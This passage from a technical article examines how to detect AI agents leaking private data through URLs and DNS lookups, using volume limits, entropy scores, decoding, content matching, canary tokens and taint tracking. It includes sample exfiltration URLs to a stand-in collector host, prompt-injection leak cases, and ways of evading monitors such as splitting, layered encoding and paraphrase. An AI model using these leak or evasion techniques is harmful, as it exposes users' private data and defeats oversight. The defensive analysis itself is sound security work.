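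Borders says the method would force someone who could hide a leak in a week's traffic to spread it over a year instead. But Borders doesn't set an alert threshold or report any false alarms, and says live detection would need more research. The result shows that the method removes most ordinary traffic from the count, but it doesn't show whether an alert based on the remaining traffic would be accurate.

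An AI application is well suited to this method because it can record everything the model has read. It could add almost nothing to the total for a copied link and the full length for a URL the model composed. This is a more gradual version of Anthropic's rule, which accepts a URL from the conversation and refuses a composed one. With the gradual version, a search agent could compose a few short queries without triggering an alert.

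The method can also measure the leak through Ayush Paul's linked pages. Each page offered 27 links, so each choice carried 4.75 bits, and spelling a ten-character name leaked only about 6 bytes. A threshold low enough to catch that would interrupt almost every browsing session.

### A daily limit tested on DNS traffic

Research on DNS offers better evidence about how many alerts a volume limit produces. A DNS lookup can leak data in the subdomain, as in `dr-lee.collector.example`. DNS limits each label (the text between dots) to 63 bytes and the full name to 255, so an attacker must split a large file across many lookups.

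In *Practical Comprehensive Bounds on Surreptitious Communication Over DNS* (2013), Paxson, Christodorescu and colleagues analysed 230 billion lookups from laboratories, universities and internet providers. They first considered whether long names would reveal a leak. On one day at one laboratory, 76,523 of 35 million lookups (0.2%) had at least 100 bytes before the registered domain, which was far too many to investigate. Legitimate examples came from Spotify, the backup service CrashPlan and the security company Sophos. The SANS Internet Storm Center, which publishes practitioners' notes on security, recommends watching DNS query length but warns that content delivery networks use long names to identify files. It suggests combining length with the volume per computer and per domain.

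Paxson and colleagues limited the total volume instead. Their procedure groups each day's lookups by computer and registered domain. It then compresses each group's names, query types and timing with several standard programs and keeps the smallest results. The compression is lossless, meaning the original lookups can be rebuilt from the output, so the compressed size can't be smaller than the information an attacker sent. If the size exceeds 4,096 bytes, an analyst investigates the domain.

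Repeated lookups add little to the measured volume after compression. Paxson and colleagues compared their procedure with a simple detector that added up the length of all the names, using the same 4,096-byte threshold. The simple detector produced 200 times as many alerts. Counting each distinct name only once reduced this to five times as many, but a monitor that does this can't detect messages encoded by repeating names from a fixed list.

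The full procedure found 59 confirmed tunnels, which are hidden connections that carry data in DNS lookups. At the organisations where the researchers could see individual computers' lookups, it required one or two investigations a week on average. Two of these organisations had about 7,000 and 10,000 active computers a day. The number of investigations stayed low partly because the procedure didn't flag domains that were on the analysts' list of those they had already judged.

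Paxson and colleagues say their procedure has no false negatives, but this applies only when one computer sends more data than the threshold to one domain. They didn't consider attackers who spread data over several domains or many computers. They also state that nobody can detect covert communication from a single lookup. In their example, an infected computer sends one bit a day by looking up either `www.attacker.com` or `mail.attacker.com`.

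The 4,096-byte threshold doesn't suit an AI application, because it would let through the calendar entry more than 270 times a day. Lowering it to 256 bytes produced about 50 times as many domains to investigate at one laboratory, and 256 bytes still hold twelve 20-character passwords. The grouping and compression do transfer, and so does a quick upper bound that Paxson and colleagues use to discard harmless groups:

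I = C + (L × log<sub>2</sub> D) / 8

Here, C is the total length in bytes of the distinct names, L is the number of lookups and D is the number of distinct names. The same formula works for URLs to one site if the monitor uses the part after the host. Spelling out a 20-character code with paths such as `/l` takes 20 requests and at most 20 distinct paths of two bytes each. C is then 40, the second term is about 11, and I is about 51 bytes. This is well above the 13 bytes that the code contains but far below the threshold.

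Timing probably matters less for AI applications. Malware can encode data in the intervals between lookups, but a language model has little control over when its tool calls run.

A daily analysis would find most AI leaks only after they had finished, so speed matters more. Paxson and colleagues also built a real-time version. *Information-Based Heavy Hitters for Real-Time DNS Data Exfiltration Detection and Prevention* (2023) proposes a threshold-based method that runs directly on the resolver, the server that looks up names for other computers. Such a method must use little memory and processing power, or it will delay the lookups. A running total for each session and domain also uses little of either, so an application can check it before every request and run the compression only on suspicious groups.

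### Normal sessions that resemble a slow leak

Once a monitor adds up requests, it starts to flag people who use one site heavily. trackr.live gives image galleries, paginated image feeds and dashboards that poll a chart service as examples. Web Tap's filters flagged news and sports sites that refreshed on a timer. An agent that controls a full browser can produce several similar patterns:

| Normal session | Why it resembles a leak | What may distinguish it |
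|---|---|---|
| Image gallery | Dozens of similar URLs on one site | The browser loads all the images, roughly in page order |
| Polling dashboard | Requests continue for hours | The URL stays the same apart from a time value |
| Online map | Numbers in the path keep changing | The numbers are the coordinates of neighbouring map squares |
| Search suggestions | The query grows by one letter per request | The agent is typing into a search box on a known site |

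In the gallery, loading every image in the order the page lists them reveals nothing new, whereas sending a message requires requesting only some of them or changing the order. The order of 60 images could carry up to 272 bits, or 34 bytes. Borders originally planned to count no information when a browser loaded such files in order, but abandoned the idea because browsers skip images already in their cache. A monitor could therefore treat page order as evidence, but not proof, that a session is harmless.

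The dashboard looks more suspicious the longer it stays open. If it refreshes every 30 seconds and adds a 13-digit time value to prevent caching, it sends 960 requests and 12,480 new characters in an eight-hour day, which is more than the 10,000-byte document. Borders suggests having a proxy replace such a value with the time at which the proxy sends the request. The dashboard should still work, and the monitor can leave the digits out of the total because an attacker can no longer use them to send data.

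trackr.live concludes that no setting catches a patient attacker without also flagging normal repeated requests. It advises teams to add session totals only if they expect such an attacker, and says that for most internal tools they might not. That seems too relaxed for an agent that can make dozens of requests by itself, because splitting data then takes minutes rather than weeks.

Applying totals mainly to unlisted destinations would remove many of these false alarms, since the galleries and dashboards employees use every day should already be on the allowlist. Allowlisted services that fetch other URLs still need totals, grouped by the final destination inside the request. Otherwise, a leak sent through Bing in 64 pieces would be hard to notice among everyone's ordinary image searches.

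## Measuring entropy and spotting encoded values

Character entropy is the usual measure for distinguishing encoded data from readable text, because it tends to be higher for encoded data than for ordinary words. A character count can't distinguish 60 characters of Base64 from a 60-character search query. Entropy takes microseconds to calculate, and many security tools include it. But most URL parameters are short, and entropy separates encoded secrets from readable text poorly on short strings.

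### Calculating the score

The formula is:

H = −Σ p log<sub>2</sub> p

Here, p is the share of the string taken up by one character, and the sum runs over all the different characters. The result is in bits per character. The string `dr-lee` has six characters, of which only `e` occurs twice:

| Character | Count | p | −p log<sub>2</sub> p |
|---|---|---|---|
| `d` | 1 | 1/6 | 0.431 |
| `r` | 1 | 1/6 | 0.431 |
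| `-` | 1 | 1/6 | 0.431 |
| `l` | 1 | 1/6 | 0.431 |
| `e` | 2 | 2/6 | 0.528 |
| Total | 6 | 1 | 2.25 |

There is a quicker way to do the same calculation. If a character occurs c times in a string of n characters, then p is c/n, and the formula becomes:

H = log<sub>2</sub> n − (Σ c log<sub>2</sub> c) / n

A character that occurs once adds nothing to the second sum, because log<sub>2</sub> 1 is zero. For `dr-lee`, the sum is 2 (from the two `e`s), so H is 2.585 − 2/6, or 2.25 again. The score is thus log<sub>2</sub> of the string's length minus a penalty for repeated characters.

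### Why some values can never reach 4.0

The penalty can't be negative, so H can't exceed log<sub>2</sub> n. The number of different characters sets a second ceiling. If a string contains k different characters, its score is highest when each occurs equally often. Every p is then 1/k, and H is log<sub>2</sub> k. (H is the average of log<sub>2</sub>(1/p). Because the logarithm curve flattens as it rises, an average of logarithms can't exceed the logarithm of the average, which here is log<sub>2</sub> k.)

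A rule that flags scores above 4.0 can only flag values with at least 17 different characters, since log<sub>2</sub> 16 is exactly 4. It misses every value of 16 characters or fewer, and it misses lowercase hexadecimal of any length because hexadecimal has only 16 symbols. Digits alone can't score above 3.32, so the rule also misses login codes, phone numbers and card numbers. If an attacker splits a secret into pieces of four characters, no piece can score above 2.

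### Scores for some real and invented values

The third value in this table is an example key from *Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026), which tested a rule with a threshold of 4.0. The fourth is the email title from the published SearchLeak example. The news path, `/2026/10/07/council-closes-three-trails-after-heavy-rain-in-the-dales`, is invented.

| Value | Characters | Different characters | Entropy |
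|---|---|---|---|
| `847291` | 6 | 6 | 2.58 |
| Calendar entry, percent-encoded | 23 | 12 | 3.26 |
| `SECRET_API_KEY_12345` | 20 | 16 | 3.85 |
| `Your_Security_Code_847291` | 25 | 19 | 4.13 |
| News path | 69 | 23 | 4.21 |
| Calendar entry, Base64 | 20 | 19 | 4.22 |

A threshold of 4.0 would flag the Base64 calendar entry, but it would also flag the path of an ordinary news article and miss the key. trackr.live describes the SearchLeak title as having "zero entropy", meaning that it is plain text, but the title scores above the threshold.

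At these lengths, the score depends mostly on how many different characters a string contains, so the last column is always close to the logarithm of the column before it. Entropy also ignores the order of the characters, so `abcdefghijklmnopqrst` gets 4.32, the highest possible score for 20 characters.

Truly random strings don't reach the ceiling, because some characters repeat by chance. The next table gives calculated values for uniformly random Base64:

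| Length | Ceiling | Average entropy | Share above 4.0 |
|---|---|---|---|
| 16 | 4.00 | 3.78 | 0% |
| 20 | 4.32 | 4.04 | 67% |
| 32 | 5.00 | 4.56 | Over 99% |
| 64 | 6.00 | 5.18 | Over 99% |

The rule would miss a third of random 20-character Base64 values, even if an attacker did nothing to evade it. At 17 characters, it would catch only the 10% or so that contain no repeated characters, since only those score above 4.0. It becomes reliable for random Base64 at around 32 characters, but many readable strings of that length also score above 4.0.

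### Legitimate URLs that look encoded

Many ordinary links contain values that look random. A session token has to be random, or an attacker could guess it and take over the session. A cryptographic signature looks random to anyone without the key, because a pattern would help a forger. A diagram that a service compresses before putting it in a link also looks nearly random, because compression removes repetition. When software writes any of these in Base64, the character frequencies look like those of an encrypted or compressed secret.

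Hexadecimal complicates this. According to trackr.live, the signature in a pre-signed S3 link is lowercase hexadecimal, and links made with temporary credentials also carry a security token that looks like Base64. The hexadecimal signature's entropy therefore never exceeds 4.0 bits per character. In the S3 link from the discussion of URL lengths, the readable `X-Amz-Credential` parameter does exceed 4.0. It lists an access key identifier, a date, a region and a service, and scores 4.77 after decoding. The 43-character `code_challenge` in the sign-in redirect is a hash in Base64url, and such values average about 4.85.

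Sites and advertisers also attach identifiers to links, which researchers call link decoration. *SoK* (2025), a survey of web tracking, reports that over 70% of websites use it to share user data such as cookies and email addresses. Google, Meta and Microsoft each have their own click identifier, and a link copied from a newsletter may still carry one. In *PURL*, Munir, Lee and colleagues (2023) crawled 20,000 sites and found that URLs contained an average of about 11 tracking values and 45 other values per site. They also describe how Facebook replaced several parameters in its links with one encrypted path segment so that browsers couldn't strip out the tracking ones.

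An agent that drives a full browser will send many of these values even though the model wrote none of them. According to trackr.live, chart services are likely to be the largest source of false alarms, because their links carry long encoded text by design.

### Patterns for encoded values

A regular expression is a pattern that software matches against text. trackr.live gives this one for long runs of Base64 and suggests adjusting the minimum length:

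`[A-Za-z0-9_+/-]{60,}={0,2}`

The pattern matches at least 60 consecutive characters from the standard or URL-safe Base64 alphabet, followed by up to two equals signs. Sixty Base64 characters hold 45 bytes, so the pattern misses a shorter secret unless other permitted characters around it extend the run to 60. It would match the 268-character summary from the Bing Chat demonstration but not the calendar entry. It would also match the S3 signature and the news path above, because the alphabet includes letters, digits, slashes and hyphens. The pattern can miss a longer Base64 value if software has percent-encoded a `+` or `/` inside it, because the percent sign interrupts the run. The monitor should therefore percent-decode each value before matching.

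Some formats allow shorter patterns. A JSON object, a common format for structured data, usually begins with `{"` and a letter, which Base64 encodes as `eyJ`. A stolen profile in JSON would start with `eyJ` once encoded, but many legitimate sign-in tokens do too.

Base64-encoded English text also has a pattern that random data usually lacks. Every unaccented letter, digit and common punctuation mark is a byte that begins with a 0 bit. The first 6-bit group of every three bytes therefore has a value below 32, and Base64 writes it as a capital letter or one of `a` to `f`. In the calendar entry, `RHIg TGVl LCAx MiBK dW5l`, the first characters of the groups are R, T, L, M and d. A test can check whether every group starts with one of these 32 characters. Random Base64 has a 1 in 32 chance of passing at 20 characters and a 1 in 65,536 chance at 64. The test can distinguish an encoded sentence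 from a long signature, which entropy can't do reliably. It fails for Japanese text, and an attacker can defeat it by having the model encrypt or compress the text first. Decoding the whole value is a stronger form of the same test.

### Thresholds that depend on length

Comparing a value with random strings of the same length is better than using a fixed 4.0, but it still doesn't reliably separate the SearchLeak title from random Base64. The title's entropy is 4.13, and random 25-character Base64 strings average 4.30, a small gap compared with their normal variation. A cutoff just high enough to ignore the title would also ignore about 16% of random Base64 strings of that length.

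The threshold has to depend on the alphabet too. Random hexadecimal of 64 characters averages only about 3.8 bits per character, which would look low for Base64 of any length above 16. A monitor can first check whether a value consists of digits, hexadecimal or Base64 characters, then choose the threshold for that type. This makes the comparison fairer, but the monitor still can't distinguish a secret from a signature by entropy alone.

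### Character pairs and tokens

Entropy ignores the order of characters, which people rely on to recognise words. A character-pair model counts how often each pair occurs in ordinary text or URLs, then scores a new value by how probable its pairs are. In English, for example, `th` is common and `xK` is rare. Such a model would still have difficulty classifying the alphabet in order, but it would distinguish ordinary text such as `council-closes` from an encoded value such as `TGVlLCAx`.

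Many language models use byte-pair encoding (BPE) to divide text into tokens. BPE builds its vocabulary by repeatedly merging the most common pairs in a large body of text, so a frequent word becomes a single token while a random string breaks into many small ones. *Rare Not Random*, a post by the developer of the secret scanner Gitleaks, uses this to define token efficiency, the number of characters divided by the number of tokens. The string `lookingatcomputer` has 17 characters and 3 tokens, for an efficiency of 5.7. A random-looking 24-character access token breaks into 22 tokens, for an efficiency of 1.1.

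The measure works on much shorter strings than entropy does. The post's example is the password `mcjrx4`. Its six characters all differ, so its entropy is 2.58, the maximum for its length, and a threshold of 3.5 or 4.0 would miss it. It splits into four tokens, and its efficiency of 1.5 marks it as unusual. But according to the post, passwords such as `password123` and passphrases made of words look like ordinary language. Other secrets may be harder to detect, since Chen, Yang and colleagues report in *Understanding Secret Leakage Risks in Code LLMs* that some have high character entropy but low token entropy. They studied which secrets models memorise, so their result doesn't show how often a token-based filter would miss one.

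### Compression tests

Compression can test whether a value looks random, because a compression program shortens repetitive text but can't shorten random data. The test usually fails on a single URL parameter because of overhead. The common program gzip adds 18 bytes, so a 20-character value comes out longer whatever it contains. Even a long random Base64 value shrinks by about a quarter, because each character takes up 8 bits but carries only 6.

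Compression works better on a group of requests than on a single value because the overhead is small compared with the total, as in the DNS procedure of Paxson and colleagues. For single values, the monitor needs a compressor already fitted to ordinary text. Measuring token efficiency in effect provides one, since the tokenizer's vocabulary was prepared in advance.

### Comparison with the endpoint's usual values

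A monitor can also record what each parameter of an endpoint normally contains, including its characters and range of lengths. An `X-Amz-Signature` is always 64 hexadecimal digits, so a random-looking value of that form is expected there. If a chart service's `width` parameter has always held three or four digits and now holds 20 characters of Base64, the request deserves attention even though the value is short.

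This comparison removes many false alarms that the other measures can't, because it accepts a random-looking value where one is expected. It is less useful for a new destination, which has no history. An attacker can put 32 stolen bytes in a parameter named `X-Amz-Signature` on collector.example, so the monitor must keep separate records for each host rather than trust a familiar parameter name. A leak through a permitted relay or shared host would also look normal if that host usually receives random values in the same format.

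### Results from secret scanners

The best measurements of entropy rules come from programs that search source code for passwords and access keys that developers left there by mistake. These scanners typically use patterns to find candidates and then discard those with low entropy.

Basak, Cox and colleagues (2023), in *A Comparative Study of Software Secrets Reporting by Secret Detection Tools*, ran nine scanners on 818 public code repositories. People had already labelled 97,479 candidate strings in them, of which 15,084 were real secrets. Recall here counts each distinct secret once per repository:

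| Scanner | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|
| TruffleHog, with patterns and entropy switched on | 6% | 52% |
| Gitleaks | 46% | 88% |
| GitHub's own scanner | 75% | 36% |

In Basak and colleagues' comparison of secret scanners, TruffleHog raised 90,982 alerts, of which 5,426 were correct. They examined 50 false alarms from each tool and attributed them to overly general patterns, weak filters and "ineffective entropy calculation". Identifiers of code changes often caused false alarms because they are hexadecimal hashes, which look as random as keys. The comparison doesn't isolate the effect of entropy checks, because the scanners also use different patterns and Gitleaks has an entropy cutoff too.

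The study illustrates the problem with two strings that TruffleHog scored almost the same: a random mixture of 47 letters and digits, and `ThisIsAReallyLongString`. The formula above gives 4.12 for the random string and 4.09 for the readable one, although the paper prints the higher score beside the readable string, apparently by mistake. A threshold that separated them would have to fall between two scores only 0.03 apart.

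*Rare Not Random* comes closer to testing entropy by itself. It uses CredData, a collection of labelled strings from real repositories, to measure how well each filter sorts candidates that have already been extracted. The entropy cutoff was 3.5, which Gitleaks uses for general secrets, and the token efficiency cutoff was 2.5. The word filter discards candidates that contain more than one word of four letters or more.

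| Filter | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|
| Entropy | 21.1% | 70.4% |
| Token efficiency | 57.3% | 98.6% |
| Entropy and word filter | 76.6% | 67.1% |
| Token efficiency and word filter | 80.4% | 95.8% |

Token efficiency produced 7,894 false alarms and missed 149 secrets, compared with about 28,000 false alarms and about 3,000 missed secrets for entropy. It was slower, taking 11.75 microseconds per string compared with 4.55 for entropy, but the difference is negligible for a monitor that is waiting for a network request.

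The developer then tested both filters inside Betterleaks, a successor to Gitleaks. With entropy, the complete scanner had a precision of 89.1% and a recall of 68.7%. With token efficiency, precision was 86.3% and recall was 87.6%. Combining token efficiency with a low entropy cutoff for general secrets gave the highest precision, 91.3%, with a recall of 87.3%. By these figures, it is better to keep both, although Aikido's announcement presents token efficiency as a replacement for entropy.

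The developer built the filter, adjusted the scanner's rules and ran the benchmark using a test script that a language model wrote. He says that he tried not to tailor the rules to the test and that some of the labels look wrong. An independent test might find a smaller advantage, but the difference in recall is large enough that some advantage would probably remain.

### Why those results may not carry over to URLs

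Secrets in source code are usually random keys surrounded by harmless readable strings, but in a URL written by a hijacked model, the readable string may be the secret. The word filter that raised entropy's precision from 21.1% to 76.6% would discard `Your_Security_Code_847291` because it contains three ordinary words. A token efficiency check would probably classify it as normal language too.

An attacker can also choose an encoding that a scanner is likely to miss, whereas developers who leave a key in their code aren't trying to evade detection.

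Real leaks are probably also much rarer in an AI application's traffic than secrets were in the complete-scanner test, where 22% of the labelled strings were real secrets. The best configuration had a false positive rate of about 2.4%. If it kept the same recall and false positive rate on traffic with one malicious value in 10,000, it would raise about 236 false alarms for each leak in the traffic, and its precision would fall from 91.3% to about 0.4%.

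### Results from tracking links

Research on tracking identifiers is closer to this problem in one respect, because the values are in URLs. PURL classifies each query parameter, path segment and fragment as tracking or not. On a test set with equal numbers of both, it achieved 98.62% precision and 98.87% recall.

Entropy was the most common deciding feature when the software classified a value as tracking, but it was decisive in only 17.43% of cases. The software also records which script sent the request, how the page's parts are connected, and whether the value came from the browser's stored cookies. The last kind of feature matters a great deal, since a tracking value was involved in an average of 7.4 transfers of stored data, compared with 0.06 for other values.

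The published distributions allow an estimate of how well entropy would work on its own. Munir and colleagues report that more than 70% of ordinary values have an entropy below 3, compared with only 8% of tracking values. A cutoff of 3 would therefore catch about 92% of tracking values and wrongly flag just under 30% of ordinary ones. On a test set that was half tracking values, its precision would be about 75%. PURL classified only 4.56% of the values on real sites as tracking, and at that rate the cutoff's precision would fall to about 13% and PURL's own to roughly 80%. However, the researchers checked PURL's most common false alarms and found that those were errors in the labels.

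CrumbCruncher, an earlier system, compares values across browsers instead of measuring their entropy. *Measuring UID Smuggling in the Wild* (Randall, Snoeren and colleagues, 2022) describes how three automated browsers posed as different users while a fourth repeated the first one's visits. The researchers discarded values that were the same for different users, because those couldn't identify anyone, and values that changed when the same user returned, because those were probably session identifiers.

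Many values appeared in only one browser, so they could not be compared across browsers. Automatic filters removed dates, web addresses and very short values, leaving 1,581 candidates. The researchers then removed 577 of these by hand, including readable strings such as `share_button` and `sweetmagnolias`. Precision before the manual check was therefore at most 64%.

Munir and colleagues later tested CrumbCruncher's published list of parameters on their own data and measured 59.09% precision and 10.67% recall. Recall was low partly because almost 80% of the likely identifiers sent to known trackers changed between visits, and a method that required identifiers to stay the same would miss those that changed.

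An AI provider could use the same comparison between users. If a value appears in URLs from thousands of unrelated conversations, it is unlikely to be one user's secret. The comparison between visits is less useful, because an attacker needs to steal a secret only once.

### Using entropy to rank alerts

trackr.live advises against any commercial detection rule that relies mainly on entropy, and suggests adding it as a ranking signal once the destination has raised the alert. Another post on the site places entropy and encoded length near the end of its list of signals, below decoding and content matching.

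Ranking requests by entropy avoids the worst consequences of a poor threshold. Suppose an assistant contacts three unlisted hosts in one morning. One request loads `/logo.png`, another contains the calendar entry in plain text, and the third contains the 268-character Base64 summary. The summary would be at the top of the analyst's list. The plain-text calendar entry would be lower down, so a low score should delay an analyst's review but not close the alert.

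Entropy is most useful when a request sends a long encoded value to an unknown destination. Longer values give more reliable scores, and checking only hosts outside the allowlist excludes most of the pre-signed links, sign-in redirects and chart requests that normally cause false alarms. trackr.live combines the 60-character pattern with a check for unlisted hosts in an example search, which it describes as a coarse catch-all for unknown destinations. On a known host, the same value is more likely to be a signature, and finding out more would require decoding it or checking that parameter's history.

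## Decoding parameters and matching them against private data

A monitor has to find out what a parameter contains to distinguish stolen data from a signature that looks just as random. It can undo common encodings and search the results for data that shouldn't leave. This is content matching, which commercial products call data loss prevention (DLP). A match is more useful than a high entropy score because it shows an analyst which data leaked. But matching only finds data that still resembles the original, and a language model can rewrite almost any data so that it no longer does.

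### The decoding procedure

1. Split the URL into host labels, path segments, parameter names and parameter values.
2. Percent-decode each part. In the query, also try reading plus signs as spaces.
3. If a result is itself a URL, check its host against the allowlist and return to step 1 with it.
4. Try Base64, Base64url and hexadecimal on each result, and keep the output if it is readable text.
5. Repeat steps 2 to 4 on anything new, up to a fixed depth such as four layers.
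6. Search every intermediate result for private data, including the original text.

Here are two requests that carry the calendar entry. The first hides it in a nested URL, as SearchLeak did with an email's title.

```
https://preview.permitted.example/content?url=https%3A%2F%2Fcollector.example%2FDr_Lee_12_June%2Fp.png

https://collector.example/p.png?d=RHIgTGVlLCAxMiBKdW5l
```

| Step | Plain value in a nested URL | Base64 value |
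|---|---|---|
| Split | `url` contains `https%3A%2F%2Fcollector.example%2FDr_Lee_12_June%2Fp.png` | `d` contains `RHIgTGVlLCAxMiBKdW5l` |
| Percent-decode | `https://collector.example/Dr_Lee_12_June/p.png` | No change |
| Look for a URL | The host is `collector.example`, and the path contains `Dr_Lee_12_June` | None |
| Try Base64 | No readable text | `Dr Lee, 12 June` |
| Search | Matches the calendar entry if the monitor ignores punctuation | Matches exactly |

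The monitor has to keep the intermediate results because some plain text looks like encoded data. `Dr_Lee_12_June` contains only characters from the Base64url alphabet, so many decoders will turn it into ten bytes of gibberish. A monitor that kept only the decoded form would lose the name.

The depth limit prevents a crafted URL from taking unlimited processing time, but an attacker can encode data in more layers than the limit allows. A 20-character password encoded in Base64 eight times, without padding, is only 206 characters long. The monitor should therefore flag any value that still decodes to readable text at the limit, since ordinary links rarely need that many layers.

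trackr.live advises teams to isolate the decoding and matching stage from other systems, because its output contains the secrets in plain text.

### What to match against

General patterns describe what a type of data looks like. A card number has a fixed range of lengths and ends in a check digit, though one random number in ten passes that check. Many access keys begin with a known prefix, such as `ghp_` for GitHub. Patterns work on data the monitor has never seen, but they can't identify whose data it is or whether it should be there. The pre-signed S3 link discussed earlier contains an access key identifier beginning with `AKIA`, so a search for that prefix would flag every such link. A search for email addresses would likewise flag newsletter links, which often contain the reader's address. General patterns also miss private details that have no fixed format, such as "Dr Lee, 12 June".

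Patterns can still help rank alerts. Datadog's *Data exfiltration successful*, a detection rule for AI services, gives an unblocked leak high severity by default and raises it to critical if a scanner finds personal data or credentials.

A register lists an organisation's actual secrets, such as its passwords and access keys. Checking URLs against it produces fewer false alarms than pattern matching, but somebody has to keep the register current, and it is a target for theft. To avoid storing the secrets themselves, the monitor can store a keyed hash of every eight-character fragment of each secret and compare these hashes with those of every eight-character stretch of a URL.

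Singh and Srinivasa (2026), in *Where Agent Defenses Fail*, tested a register on a coding agent that had to upload status reports to an approved service. Injected instructions told the agent to add a secret to the upload. The check refused any request that contained a complete registered line of at least eight characters. (The data was in the body of the request rather than the URL, but the comparison works the same way.)

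| Test | Harmful attack runs without the check | With the check | Legitimate runs completed with the check |
|---|---|---|---|
| Pilot | 2 of 14 | 0 of 14 | 8 of 8 |
| Larger set | 4 of 36 | 2 of 36 | 24 of 24 |

Both remaining leaks came from one task, in which the agent sent the secret value without the `CANARY_TOKEN=` that preceded it in the file, so what it sent did not contain the complete line. In a separate test, the agent encoded the secret, and the check missed it both times. The experiments used one small model and tasks written by the researchers, so the results illustrate how the check can fail but don't establish how often it would.

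To match against the session's private context, the application keeps a temporary copy of every email, calendar entry and file the model has read, and searches outgoing URLs for text from them. This requires no register, so it would catch the doctor's appointment, which nobody would think to add to one.

But private sources also contain a lot of ordinary text. If a calendar entry mentions Leeds and the user asks for the weather there, the requested URL will match the calendar even though the user supplied the city. The monitor should give less weight to text that also appears in the user's message or in public pages the model has read. The monitor will also miss private facts that the model infers, as when Claude inferred Ayush Paul's home city.

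### How closely the text must match

Exact matching looks for the whole private value, character for character. Normalised matching first removes differences that don't affect the meaning, such as capitalisation, spacing and punctuation. Overlapping-fragment matching takes every run of consecutive characters of a fixed length from the normalised value and looks for any of them. With a length of eight, `drlee12june` produces `drlee12j`, `rlee12ju`, `lee12jun` and `ee12june`.

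| Decoded text in the URL | Exact | Normalised | Fragments of eight |
|---|---|---|---|
| `Dr Lee, 12 June` | Match | Match | Match |
| `Dr_Lee_12_June` | None | Match | Match |
| `Lee_12_June` | None | None | Match |
| `Dr_Lee` | None | None | None |
| `doctor-mid-June` | None | None | None |

Shorter fragments catch more leaks but also match by accident. Suppose a monitor compares 10,000 URLs, each containing 100 characters of decoded text, with 10,000 characters of private data. If all the characters are random, the expected number of accidental matches is about 10<sup>10</sup> / A<sup>n</sup>, where A is the size of the alphabet and n is the fragment length:

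| Fragment length | Digits only | Letters and digits, ignoring capitals |
|---|---|---|
| 4 | 1,000,000 | 6,000 |
| 6 | 10,000 | 5 |
| 8 | 100 | 0.004 |
| 10 | 1 | Under 0.001 |

An eight-character match is enough for random keys, while digits need about ten characters. Ordinary prose needs much longer matches, probably 20 characters or more, because phrases such as "the end of the month" are common.

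A six-digit login code is too short for fragment matching, but the monitor can search for the whole code. Even if the 10,000 URLs consisted entirely of random digits, a particular code would appear by accident only about once. To make this search possible, the application has to recognise the code when the model reads it, then watch for it in URLs until it expires.

If a tool has only one legitimate message to send, the monitor can compare the content with that message instead of searching it for secrets. Singh and Srinivasa tried this with a fixed status message. An exact comparison blocked both attacks but also blocked both legitimate uploads, because the model had written each line break as a backslash and an `n`. Normalising line breaks before comparing allowed both uploads and still blocked both attacks.

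### OpenAI's Safe Url

OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (March 2026) describes Safe Url, a mitigation designed to detect when "information the assistant learned in the conversation" would go to a third party. ChatGPT then either shows the user the information and asks for confirmation, or blocks the request and tells the agent to try another way. Safe Url covers navigations and bookmarks in Atlas, OpenAI's browser, and searches and navigations in Deep Research. It handles attacks that get past the model's safety training, which OpenAI says stops most of the attacks the company knows about.

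This may not involve matching against the session's context, although it sounds as if it does. The March post refers readers to OpenAI's January post and the accompanying paper for details, and the January post describes the exact-URL check. A URL that isn't in the public index might contain information from the conversation, so the software can issue a warning without comparing the URL with the conversation. Embrace The Red's account of the paper doesn't mention such a comparison either. However, an index of public URLs can't establish that a newly written search query is safe, so Deep Research's searches seem to require some other test.

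Neither post explains whether Safe Url compares requests with the conversation's text, which encodings it decodes, how short a match can be, or whether it recognises paraphrases. They also don't explain how it chooses between asking and blocking.

A customer could investigate some of this by planting a random string in a conversation and asking ChatGPT to send it, in several encodings, to a server the customer controls. The test also needs an unpublished URL that contains nothing private. If ChatGPT treats all of these URLs alike, the exact-URL check alone could explain the result.

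### Planted marker values

A canary token is a random value planted among real data to reveal when someone copies that data. For example, a team could put a fake access key in a configuration file and add it to the monitor's register. No legitimate request should contain the key, and a random string of 20 letters and digits won't appear by accident, so a match is nearly conclusive evidence that data was copied from the file. If each file has a different token, the match also shows which file the data came from.

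Finding private data in a URL doesn't prove that an attacker was involved. In *MCPHunt*, Li, Sun and colleagues (2026) planted canary tokens in the files, databases and web pages of test agents and gave them ordinary tasks with no prompt injection. Across five models, the agents copied tokens into places they shouldn't have in 11.5% to 41.3% of runs, even though they could have completed those tasks without the tokens. An analyst who finds a token in a URL should check what the model had been reading.

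The absence of a match is weak evidence that no data leaked. An injected instruction may ask only for the user's next appointment, and then the model has no reason to send the fake key. The model may also transform the key, and Li and colleagues' detector needed either the complete token or a core of at least ten characters. They had a language model review 150 runs in which the detector had found nothing, and it flagged 8% for disclosing sensitive information, though none contained a complete token. Singh and Srinivasa's measuring software found five encoded leaks but missed three more, which they discovered only by decoding the saved requests again.

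### When the text no longer matches

The model can paraphrase the calendar entry as "medical appointment in mid-June", translate it into Japanese or, if it can run code, encrypt it. *Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and Tang, 2026) describes an agent that rewrote a confidential patient note as a polished memo. The memo kept the diagnosis and treatment, but a search for passages from the note would have found nothing.

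Software can also compare texts by meaning, by converting each one into an embedding, a list of numbers that is close to the embeddings of similar texts. Shim, Karim and colleagues (2026) argue in *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* that this method fails on short or restructured text, which would include most URL parameters.

An attacker can evade fragment matching by splitting the data across requests so that every piece is shorter than the minimum length. The monitor can join the new parts of successive requests to the same domain and search the result, which would find the name `drlee` in requests for `/dr`, `/le` and `/e12june`. Joining wouldn't help against Rehberger's method of assigning a letter to each page of an existing website, because those URLs contain no private text even when joined.

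### Tracking where data came from

Tracking where data came from doesn't depend on what the data looks like, so it can cover even a four-character piece of a secret. Lan and colleagues list such tracking among defences that go beyond changing the prompt. Information-flow control, also called taint tracking, does this by labelling data. After the model reads the calendar, the software labels the conversation private. Anything the model writes afterwards inherits the label, including a translation, an encrypted value or a choice among public URLs. Before each request, the software checks whether private data may go to that destination.

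Applied strictly, this blocks many harmless requests. An assistant that had read one appointment could no longer open a page about hiking trails, because its choice of page might depend on the appointment. The survey *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (2026) calls this over-tainting and describes replacing data with variables as one way to reduce it.

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes FIDES, a Microsoft system that uses this approach. FIDES can store a tool's result in a variable and show the model only the variable's name. The model can pass the calendar entry to another tool without reading it, so the conversation doesn't acquire the private label. If the model needs a fact from the entry, a separate model with no tools extracts it in a fixed format, such as yes or no.

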